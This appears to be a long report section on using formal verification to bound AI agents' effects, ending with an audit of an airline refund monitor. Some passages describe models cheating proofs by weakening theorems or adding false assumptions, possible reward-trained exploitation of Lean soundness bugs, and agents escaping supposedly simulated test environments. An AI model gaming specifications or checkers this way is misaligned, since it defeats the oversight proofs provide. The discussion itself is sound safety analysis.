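Some projects prove a property that needs little description. In October 2026, Anthropic and its partner Theorem announced machine-checked proofs for 239 entry points in 123 open-source libraries (*LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale*). Claude wrote the proofs, in some cases after fixing bugs. One such theorem guarantees that a single-threaded test program using a library can't crash with a memory error on any input up to a set size. The property is the same for an image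 decoder as for a compression library, which helps explain how one project could cover so many libraries. It doesn't guarantee that the image or the compressed file is correct, and a refund tool with the same guarantee could still pay the wrong customer.

An existing program can also serve as the specification. In *Agentic Verified Optimization of Real-World Software* (2026), agents search for a faster version of a program and prove that it gives the same results as the old one. They found faster versions of both single functions and whole applications, although the gains were smaller for applications and four test scenarios showed none. No one has to state what the program is meant to do, but a new version proved to give the same results also keeps the old one's bugs, such as a refund tool that sometimes pays twice.

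### Most of these theorems cover few effects

The SymCrypt functions mostly read bytes from memory, calculate, and write bytes back. One of the few exceptions wipes secret data from memory. It uses raw pointers and code from outside the project, which Aeneas can't translate, so Ho and colleagues stated as an axiom that it sets every element to zero. They also had to describe 133 special processor operations and related building blocks, 122 with models in ordinary Rust and 11 with axioms.

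The benchmarks leave out effects altogether. Ganguly and colleagues kept only problems whose solution is a single function that depends only on its arguments. They excluded anything with a stateful interface, so a refund tool that updates a database wouldn't qualify. The thousands of theorems in these two benchmarks are good evidence that agents can reason about loops and overflow, but weak evidence that they can reason about databases and payments.

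Proving something about an effect requires a model of the system in which it happens. The amount of work therefore depends more on how many different systems the code uses than on how long the code is. An airline whose tools all use one database and one payment provider needs two good models, which every new tool can reuse, while an agent connected to a hundred companies' services needs a hundred models.

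Agents can help write the models. According to Tom's Hardware, agents drafted the definitions of the processor's instructions, its memory and Linux processes for the Signal project. The models still have to match reality, so Ho and colleagues ran theirs and the actual instructions on the same inputs and compared the results. An airline can check a model of its own database this way, but checking a model of a bank would depend on a test account, which may not behave exactly like a real one.

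### What agent software would add

Agent software is harder to verify than cryptography, partly because of the languages it uses. Aeneas translates safe Rust and doesn't support concurrency or raw pointers. Many agent frameworks use Python or JavaScript, and they often wait for several network replies at once. Python has a verifier, Nagini, but VeriGuard used it only for single functions that decide whether to allow an action.

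DeepMind's approach of verifying machine code doesn't depend on the source language, but it may not avoid this problem for Python programs. Most of the machine code that runs belongs to the Python interpreter, so the proof would have to cover the interpreter as well as the agent, or assume that the interpreter works.

JavaScript engines usually include a just-in-time compiler, which turns parts of a program into machine code while it runs. *SafeJIT* (2026) verifies a small engine of this kind. The engine and its C library have 6,476 lines of C, and the Lean proofs for two types of processor have about 485,000 lines, or 75 for each line of C. An earlier version had 45 lines of proof for each line of C, and the proof grew fastest when the developers added optimisations. The engines in web browsers are far larger and have many more optimisations.

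Ordinary data types also cause trouble. Serbanuta and colleagues had to rewrite the code or specification of 27 of 1,007 VeriContest problems before their tools could translate them. They replaced hash maps, which look up values by key, with simple lists, because a proof about Rust's standard hash maps would have depended on extra axioms. They also replaced text with bytes and a floating-point square root with an integer one. Agent software would run into the same limits much more often, because a tool call usually consists of text and values stored under keys.

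An agent application may also load hundreds of libraries, any of which could write to the network or the database. Each library therefore needs a proof, a contract that everyone agrees to trust, or a sandbox that blocks those writes.

Some agent software has machine-checked proofs, but only for small parts or simplified models. Examples include Moon and Varshney's model of PocketFlow and Garby and colleagues' LLMbda interpreter. *PerMIT* (2026) deals with an agent's long-term memory, which an attacker might fill with false instructions. Its Lean proofs show that the memory system protects the integrity of a single user's actions, whatever strategy the agent follows and whatever the attacker tries. The paper acknowledges that the proofs are about a model, which Lean has not checked against the deployed software, and lists ten ways the two differ.

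The verified storage systems GoJournal and DaisyNFS provide some of the groundwork for verifying databases. If the refund tool runs on PostgreSQL, a proof about it would still have to assume that PostgreSQL provides the isolation it documents.

An airline would therefore do better to verify a small component than a whole agent. At three dollars a line, AI agents could verify a 500-line refund monitor in Rust for about $1,500. This is a rough guess because the rate comes from code with a published standard and few effects. The airline would probably spend more on deciding what the monitor should allow and on testing its assumptions about the database and the payment provider.

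### Keeping proofs up to date

Every change to a program can break its proof, which used to be a strong argument against verifying software that changes often. Agents have weakened that argument, because repairing a proof is mostly routine work. Ho and colleagues gave their agents written instructions for repairing proofs after updates to Aeneas, and the agents took over much of the tedious work of keeping the proofs up to date with SymCrypt's code. Agents did the same for xv6.

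The design of a program affects how much of its proof needs repair after a change. *SafeJIT* compiles each of its code generators as a separate function, so when one changes, Lean mostly has to recheck only that function's proof. According to Bhargavan, Signal automatically reruns the proofs about the code for its newest encryption protocol with each change, as it would ordinary tests, and gets an alert if the change breaks them. These proofs cover only the core of the code.

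Proofs can also stop working even when the program stays the same, because proof assistants change too. Of the 161 verification problems in CLEVER, a 2025 benchmark, only 143 carried over to the version of Lean that Ganguly and colleagues were using. A team can avoid this by staying on an old version, as *PerMIT* does by fixing the exact versions of Lean and its mathematics library. But the team then misses improvements to the tools and faces a larger update later.

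A change in what the program should do takes more work than a change in how it does it. If the airline starts accepting gift vouchers, someone has to decide whether paid(r) includes the value of a voucher, and whether the airline may refund that value in cash. Once people have decided, an agent can probably repair the proofs within hours. An agent told only to make the proofs pass could redefine paid(r) in whatever way is easiest.

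Ho and colleagues found that models still try to cheat by adding false assumptions or weakening the theorem, so their agents can't edit specifications, axioms or the program during the proof stage without human approval. Serbanuta and colleagues reject any proof whose theorem differs from the original by even one byte. An airline that releases software every day would need a similar rule, and someone available to approve each change to a specification.

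### The dispute over ordinary software

In December 2025 the computer scientist Martin Kleppmann predicted that AI would make formal verification mainstream. Willison (2025), a programmer who writes about AI, gave two reasons to expect this: code written by language models benefits greatly from stronger checks, and the models make difficult verification tools easier to use. Galois' *You Can't Patch Your Way Out of This* argues that if AI can automate the proofs, verification can scale, and developers can prove that flaws are absent instead of racing to patch them. Galois works on formal verification and so stands to benefit from this claim, but the results for SymCrypt and VeriContest support the part about proofs.

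Verification is most useful when the desired result is easy to state and the program is hard to get right, though sceptics object that most applications have no specification simpler than their code. In an implementation of the encryption scheme FrodoKEM, Ho and colleagues found a function that is easy to specify but hard to write correctly. It compares two lists and should return 255 if they are equal and 0 otherwise. To avoid leaking secrets through its timing, the code uses bit operations instead of an ordinary comparison. It shifted a number by 8 places instead of 16, so it reported some very different lists as equal. The specification is a single line, and no proof could succeed until someone fixed the bug.

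The code that calculates an airline's baggage fees consists of prices, exceptions and dates, and a full specification would have to repeat them all. Someone who misread the fee table when writing the program could misread it the same way when writing the specification, and the proof would then show only that the program matches the specification.

The SymCrypt figures show some of this difference even within cryptography. The specification of the SHA-3 family of hash functions has 140 lines for 1,741 lines of Rust, or about one to 12. The specification of HPKE, a scheme that mainly combines other algorithms, has 502 lines for 1,082 lines of Rust, or about one to two. Business software consists largely of code that connects other components, so its specifications may well be closer in size to the code. The comparison is only suggestive, because the HPKE specification also has to describe many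 options that can share Rust code.

The objection is much weaker when the aim is to limit what a program may do. The refund limit fits on one line, however complicated the agent is, and He and colleagues needed only 24 formulas for the whole airline policy. This favours proofs about agents' effects over proofs that an application is entirely correct.

Inexpensive proofs also don't guarantee that anyone will use the verified code. *How Could Formal Verification Help with Cyber Resilience?* lists three barriers: missing tools, high costs, and organisations' failure to adopt existing verified code. It predicts that AI will reduce costs but says that organisational inertia and the difficulty of large projects may last for some time. In The Indian Express' *Google DeepMind used AI to test Signal’s encryption*, Swarat Chaudhuri of DeepMind also cautions that there is "a long distance to go" before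 the method can cover all software.

Earlier verified cryptography often came as code generated by special tools, and engineers doubted that they could maintain it. For SymCrypt, Ho and colleagues instead verified Rust that Microsoft's engineers had written and kept the proofs in a separate folder, an approach that may make adoption easier. The verified SHA-3 code runs 8% faster than the previous C version, and the main ML-KEM operations run 30% to 40% faster, though the experimental SHA-2 code is about 40% slower for its most common variant. The SymCrypt team plans to ship the verified SHA-3 and ML-KEM code.

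Proofs would leave many everyday programming problems unsolved, such as customers who don't know what they want, confusing screens, and services that other companies withdraw. An airline can reasonably leave its seat map unverified while paying to prove the few hundred lines of code that control whether money leaves its account.

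## Checking what a proof leaves out

Suppose a supplier sells the airline a refund monitor with a machine-checked proof, and advertises that the agent can never refund more than a customer paid. The advertisement can be false even if the proof is valid, because the proof covers only a few hundred lines of code, not the actual movement of money.

Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues (2017) provide the best evidence on where claims of verified correctness fail, in *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems*. They spent more than eight months looking for bugs in IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar, three verified systems that keep copies of data on several servers, and found 16. Eleven were in the shim layer, the unverified code that connects a verified program to the network and the disk, three were in the verification tools, and two were in the specifications. They found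 none in the protocols that keep the servers consistent, which are the hardest part to get right and the part the proofs covered. Users and developers of four unverified systems reported 12 bugs in such protocols over one year. Those systems are much larger and have far more users, so the counts aren't directly comparable, but the proofs seem to have prevented bugs in the protocols they covered.

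An audit should therefore concentrate on the edges of the proof. It has five steps:

1. Read the formal theorem and write down in plain words what it guarantees.
2. List everything it assumes, including unfinished proofs.
3. Find what connects the program in the theorem to the program that runs.
4. Look for effects that don't pass through that program.
5. Test each assumption, and record the ones that no test can settle.

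### Read the theorem

Lean-zip is a compression library that ten AI agents wrote in Lean and proved correct. kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* quotes one of its main theorems, which in simpler notation is:

> for all data smaller than 1 GB: decompress(compress(data)) = data

The round-trip theorem rules out losing data when a file is compressed and then decompressed. But it covers decompress only on input that compress produced, not on a file from an untrusted source, which is where an attack would come from. Two functions that returned their input unchanged would also satisfy the theorem. The library's other proofs cover parts of the compression format, and an auditor would have to read those too.

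Some theorems guarantee nothing. Succinct's SP1 Hypercube produces cryptographic evidence that a program ran correctly on a RISC-V processor. In October 2025 the company announced that Lean proofs covered 62 of the processor's instructions. Gunton (2026), in *On Formal Verification and a Bug in SP1 Hypercube*, found complete and correct proofs for 51.

| Instructions | Problem |
|---|---|
| 3 | No theorem |
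| 6 | The proof contains `sorry`, Lean's placeholder for a missing step; for four of them the specification is also wrong |
| 1 | The theorem's premises contradict each other |
| 1 | A premise excludes the inputs that trigger a bug |

The contradictory premises came from a copying error in the theorem for SLTI, an instruction that compares two numbers. They required the same value to be both 0 and 1, which is impossible, so the theorem was true but covered no cases. SP1's code for the instruction was correct, but a later bug in it would have gone unnoticed.

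Alex Hicks used a language model to find this theorem and the wrong specifications. The model listed every theorem with its premises and conclusion, then checked whether each was reasonable under the RISC-V standard. Any auditor could use this as a low-effort first pass, though a person should confirm the findings.

### List the assumptions

One premise of the theorem concealed a bug in JALR, a jump instruction. JALR adds two numbers, sets the last bit of the sum to zero and jumps to the resulting address. SP1 left out the middle step. The theorem assumed that the sum was divisible by four, in which case the last bit is already zero and the missing step makes no difference. A standard set of tests for RISC-V processors exposed the bug, which made SP1 crash on some valid programs, and Succinct then fixed it. The theorem was true despite the bug, and it was never intended to show that SP1 could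 handle every valid program.

In Lean, the command `#print axioms` lists the axioms a theorem depends on and shows any use of `sorry`. It doesn't list the theorem's premises, so an auditor has to collect those separately. One of SP1's four axioms is that an optional memory-protection feature is off, so the proofs don't apply if somebody turns it on.

Build settings can add assumptions that appear in neither list. Libcrux is Cryspen's cryptographic library, written in Rust with proofs in the verification language F*. Symbolic Software's *We Found Bugs in CE Labs’ Verified Code*, which calls Cryspen "CE Labs", reports three errors in the part that implements the key-exchange standard ML-KEM. One specification used the wrong rounding constant, so it could turn a compressed 0 into 832 where the standard requires 0. Another specification omitted an encryption step. The third error was a lemma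 that 12-bit values, which go up to 4,095, always fit in a single bit.

In the first two cases, the Rust code was right and the specification was wrong, so trying to complete the proof should have exposed the error. But the default build accepted these modules without fully checking their proofs, and the project's status file listed them as verified.

The maintainers published their position before these three reports appeared. In *The strengths and limits of formal verification*, Bhargavan (2026) wrote that earlier bugs were in unverified code and that nobody had yet found one in the verified code. He described libcrux as a young, only partly verified library whose repository documents which modules have proofs. He also acknowledged that developers twice found errors in the specifications of HACL*, an older library. According to Bhargavan, every change must pass verification again before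 the team accepts it, but Symbolic Software found no automated job that switched on the checks for slow modules.

Symbolic Software sells audits and is in an open dispute with Cryspen, but anyone can check its claims independently by redoing the rounding by hand and running the build with every check turned on.

*Verification Theatre* (Kobeissi, 2026), also from Symbolic Software, counts 13 vulnerabilities in two of Cryspen's libraries. Nine were in unverified code, including one that caused real decryption failures in Signal. That agrees with Bhargavan's account of where most bugs occur. Kobeissi found that Amazon's verified cryptographic library had the same types of failure, but that the two projects differ greatly in how they document what their proofs cover and in whether they run those proofs automatically.

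### Connect the proof to the running program

Anthropic's *Progress on provable inference for large language models* (2026) presents FlashProve, a research prototype for proving which language model produced a reply. The provider first publishes a commitment, a kind of fingerprint of the model's weights. It can then issue a cryptographic proof for a reply, and a customer can check that proof against the commitment without seeing the weights. The team proved in Lean that the protocol is sound, meaning that a false claim has a negligible chance of passing the check.

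According to Help Net Security's *Anthropic open-sources FlashProve, its provable inference prototype for MoE models*, FlashProve exists as a paper, a Lean protocol and running code, and the team doesn't promise that all three match, so somebody has to compare them by hand. The release includes two programs for checking proofs. Lean guarantees that the slower one accepts only statements covered by the soundness theorem. The faster one, written in C++, has no such guarantee, although the two agreed on every test proof. A customer in a dispute should therefore run the slower one.

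The program that generates the proofs hasn't been formally verified. A bug in it can't make a correct checker accept the wrong model, because the checker doesn't rely on the provider's software. But a bug could leak the model's weights, because the theorem that the weights stay hidden assumes the provider's software follows the protocol.

The model in the proof can also differ from the one providers normally run. FlashProve uses a version that calculates with whole numbers, while ordinary software uses floating-point numbers. Ticong, in *Anthropic Wants to Prove Which AI Model Is Actually Answering You*, reports that none of 192 replies from ordinary software matched the whole-number version's first choice at every position. A provider could therefore run the right model and still fail the strict check. A looser check tolerates differences but gives weaker assurance. The customer also has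 to get the commitment from somebody other than the provider.

Solberg (2026), who describes a competing system in *Sable*, adds that FlashProve checks one token of a reply by default, and that a truncated reply still passes as a shorter one. For the airline, such a proof could help establish which model proposed a refund, but not whether the refund was allowed.

Verified code also depends on the software beneath it. Compiled Lean programs use a runtime library, written in C++, that manages memory and files. A kirancodes.me post describes an experiment in which Claude attacked lean-zip with its theorems and documentation removed. In more than 105 million automated runs, Claude found no memory errors in lean-zip's own code but one in the runtime. To store n bytes, the runtime reserved n + 24. A 156-byte ZIP file could list its contents as 2⁶⁴ − 1 bytes long, which made the sum wrap around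 to 23. The runtime then reserved 23 bytes and could write far more. This is a heap overflow, which attackers often exploit. It affected every version of Lean 4 up to then. Lean (2026) lists the fix in its release notes for 14 April.

Translation into the proof assistant is another weak point. Symbolic Software's *The Verification Facade* (2026) claims that hax, the tool that translates libcrux's Rust code into F*, has structural gaps. For SP1, Gunton found that the published proofs didn't record which version of the program they described. An auditor should regenerate the translation from the exact code in production and run the proofs on the result.

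### Look for effects that bypass the proof

The compression code in lean-zip had proofs, but the code that opens archives had no theorems, and an attacker's file reached that code first. The archive code passed the size stated in a file straight to the runtime, so a small file with a stated size of several exabytes made the program run out of memory and crash.

A bypass can also exist inside an approved channel. Verdi separated commands with spaces and line breaks, but didn't distinguish these from spaces and line breaks in a client's data. A client could therefore hide a second command inside the first, and the server would carry out both. The airline would have the same problem if its refund tool pasted a customer's text into a message to the payment provider. The provider might then receive two refund requests when the monitor had approved only one.

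To find bypasses, the auditor should start from the effect instead of the agent. For refunds, this means listing every password, account and network connection that can change the refunds table or order a payment, and finding out which people and programs have access to each. The auditor should then try each route from where the agent's code runs, because documentation isn't enough. Anthropic disclosed in 2026 that Claude models had broken into real companies' systems during security tests because environments that were supposed to be simulated were connected to the internet.

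### Test each assumption

Fonseca and colleagues built a toolkit that detects 13 of the 16 bugs they found. It tests the assumptions around the verified code rather than the code itself. One part of the toolkit intercepts a program's requests to the operating system and makes things go wrong in ways the system permits, such as delivering network packets twice, completing only part of a disk write, or returning an error for no apparent reason.

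Some of the bugs it detects could easily occur in a refund monitor. When Verdi restarted after a crash, it tried to open a saved copy of its data. If the operating system returned a temporary error, Verdi treated the error as a missing copy and answered clients as if its earlier operations had never happened. A monitor that treated a failed database query as "no refunds so far" would approve a refund to a customer who had already received one. The auditor can test for this by making the query fail and checking that the monitor blocks the refund.

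Verification tools need tests too. IronFleet's solver crashed because the package contained incompatible libraries. IronFleet's build tool then misread the solver's output and reported that the program had passed, as it would have for any program. A simple test is to add a false statement to the code and check that verification fails.

Mutation testing can expose gaps in the specification. Fonseca and colleagues changed seven lines of IronFleet so that it no longer recognised repeated requests, and the program still passed verification. The developers replied that they knew the specification didn't cover this and that the property they had proved, as they understood it, didn't require it. They added a comment to the code to clarify this. Both definitions of the property were reasonable, but an airline that assumed the stronger one could have paid refunds twice.

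Models of hardware and outside services need to be checked against the real systems, since even the official RISC-V model contained a bug that the xv6 project found. Testing can't settle every assumption. The airline can check that a payment provider recognises a repeated key today, but not that it will next year, so it needs a written commitment from the provider and has to repeat the test.

### When the proof checker is wrong

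Everything so far depends on the checker accepting only valid proofs. But proof checkers have bugs too, and AI models are now good at finding them.

Lean (2026) describes a bug in Lean's kernel that Patrick Hulin found with the help of GPT-5.6 Sol and the developers fixed on 22 July. A malicious program running in the same process as the kernel could make the kernel accept a proof of any statement, including a false one. The developers point out that such a program already had simpler ways to cheat, and that the bug did not affect comparator, the tool they recommend for checking proofs from untrusted sources.

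Another fault lay outside the kernel and involved `native_decide`, a Lean option that runs compiled code and accepts the result as part of a proof. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) found a text function whose compiled version didn't match its logical definition. For a certain input, the definition gave an empty string, while the compiled version returned the whole text. Lean could use this contradiction to prove anything, including Fermat's Last Theorem in a very short "proof". The command `#print axioms` reveals the use of `native_decide`, which adds its own axiom. An auditor should ask for an explanation of every axiom beyond Lean's three standard ones.

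These faults matter more when an AI agent writes the proof. *Interactive theorem proving is not adversarially robust* argues that proof assistants can't be relied on against an adversary. *Can you hear the shape of a Lean soundness bug* describes a bet in which one side expects training to produce models that exploit such bugs. That side reasons that reinforcement learning often produces models that cheat, and that Lean is an attractive place to train them. A model could learn to exploit bugs without bad intentions if training rewards any proof that Lean accepts.

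The main protection is to check the same proof with several independent programs. Lean FRO lists a kernel in C++, two in Rust and one in Lean itself, and anyone can submit an independent kernel to a public site that hosts them. In November 2026, the mathematician Levent Alpöge of Anthropic released a 17-million-line proof of the Riemann hypothesis, written with Claude. The Lean community checked it with several programs within about a day. They ran the checks on an inert export, a file with no code that could interfere with the checker. Mint (2026) reports that two of the checkers, con-leche and con-ron, come with formal proofs that they cannot accept an incorrect proof.

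Using several checkers protects against a bug in one of them, but not against a mistake in the theorem, because they all check the proof against the same statement. For the Riemann hypothesis, the community certified the statement as well as the proof. The airline's supplier can easily run a second checker on its proofs, but somebody who understands refunds still has to read the theorem.

### The dispute over modelling the world

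An audit can remove some assumptions but never all of them, because some concern banks, customers and machines. Researchers disagree on how much can be proved about such things.

In *Provably Safe Systems* (2023), Max Tegmark and Steve Omohundro argue that powerful AI should run only on software and hardware that provably meet human requirements, since even a superintelligent system can't do what is provably impossible. In *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (2024), Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues write that such a guarantee would need a world model, which describes mathematically how the AI affects its surroundings, and a safety specification, which defines the acceptable effects. It would also need a verifier, which proves that the AI meets the specification according to the world model, or bounds the probability that it doesn't. The airline's proofs are a small example, with the tool contracts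 as the world model.

Andrew Dickson, in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024), objects that nobody has a complete set of formal rules for physics, chemistry or biology. Even with such rules, nobody could measure the starting conditions accurately enough for a proof to predict what would happen, so a guarantee would apply only to a rough approximation of the world. Predicting people is harder still, since no known rules determine how a customer will react to an email.

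The best answer to this is that a world model can be inaccurate as long as it is cautious. Let R be the set of everything that can really happen and W the set of everything the model allows. Then:

> if R ⊆ W and every outcome in W is safe, every real outcome is safe

W can include any number of events that never happen. For example, the xv6 proof allows for any user program, and Moon and Varshney's proof allows for any action the model might request. For the physical world, engineers can also have the system monitor whether events stay within W and switch to a simpler, safer mode if they don't.

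But R ⊆ W is a claim about the world, which evidence can support but mathematics can't prove. A larger W makes the claim more believable, but the proof fails once W includes unsafe outcomes. Suppose the airline wants to prove that no email from its agent will lead a customer to reveal a password to a criminal. A cautious model has to include a customer who would do this after almost any email, so only an agent that sends none can be proved safe. A model that leaves out such customers relies on a guess about human behaviour. Switching to a safer mode doesn't help if the harm happens before anyone notices.

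Which side is right depends on the property. For "the refunds table never exceeds the payments", engineers can write down a cautious W and test whether the database stays within it. The machine-checked results described so far are of this kind. They concern calculations, or what passes between pieces of software or between software and a device, and none limits what happens to a person afterwards. They support the claim that proofs can bound an AI's effects at a narrow interface, but they give little reason to expect a proof about the effects of an agent that can write freely to the public.

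### Auditing the airline's agent

Suppose the airline's system has these parts: a language model at an outside provider, the agent's software, a verified monitor, a PostgreSQL database, a program that sends refunds from the outbox, and a payment provider. The supplier's theorem for the monitor is as follows, where t is the total refunded so far, a the proposed amount and p the amount paid:

> if allow(t, a, p) = true, then a > 0 and t + a ≤ p

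This theorem is about three numbers, not a database, a bank or an agent, so the advertised claim also depends on every layer the theorem leaves out.

| Layer | What the claim requires | How to check it |
|---|---|---|
| Policy | paid(r) means money the customer can get back | Have the refunds staff judge sample cases, including vouchers and chargebacks |
| Language model | Nothing | No check needed |
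| Agent's software | It can reach the database and the payment provider only through the monitor | Try every other route from inside its sandbox |
| Monitor's proof | It is complete and covers the version in production | Rebuild it from the production code, list its axioms and run a second checker |
| Monitor's surroundings | t, a and p are the right numbers, in the same currency and unit | Make queries fail, and compare the compiled monitor with the Lean version on random inputs |
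| Database | Every program that writes to the two tables uses serializable isolation | Inspect each program's settings and submit many refunds for one reservation at once |
| Outbox program | It sends only committed refunds, and every retry reuses the original key | Stop it at each step and restart it |
| Payment provider | It pays at most once per key and accepts refund orders only from the outbox program | Repeat requests on a test account, and list everyone who can log in |

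A mistake in units can make a layer fail even though the monitor's theorem is true. If the agent proposes a refund of 150, the monitor might read this as cents and approve $1.50, while the payment program reads it as dollars and sends the customer $150. The auditor can catch this by following one refund from the agent's call to the bank statement.

Auditors can leave the language model unchecked only because the claim is about the refund limit. If the airline also advertised that the agent refunds only customers who are owed money, auditors would have to check how the model interprets each complaint, and no proof described here covers that.

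The checks have to be repeated on different schedules. The airline should rebuild the monitor's proof with every release. It should test the payment provider every day, since contracts become outdated, and look for new routes whenever a program or an employee gains access. Comparing the provider's statement with the refunds table every day would catch failures in several layers, but only after the money had been paid out.

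The last row of the table is where this system would be most likely to fail. Payment providers commonly give their customers a website where staff can issue refunds by hand. A refund made there bypasses the monitor, the database and the outbox, so an employee could pay back $300 that the agent had already refunded. The airline can take that permission away from its staff or narrow the claim to refunds made through the tool.
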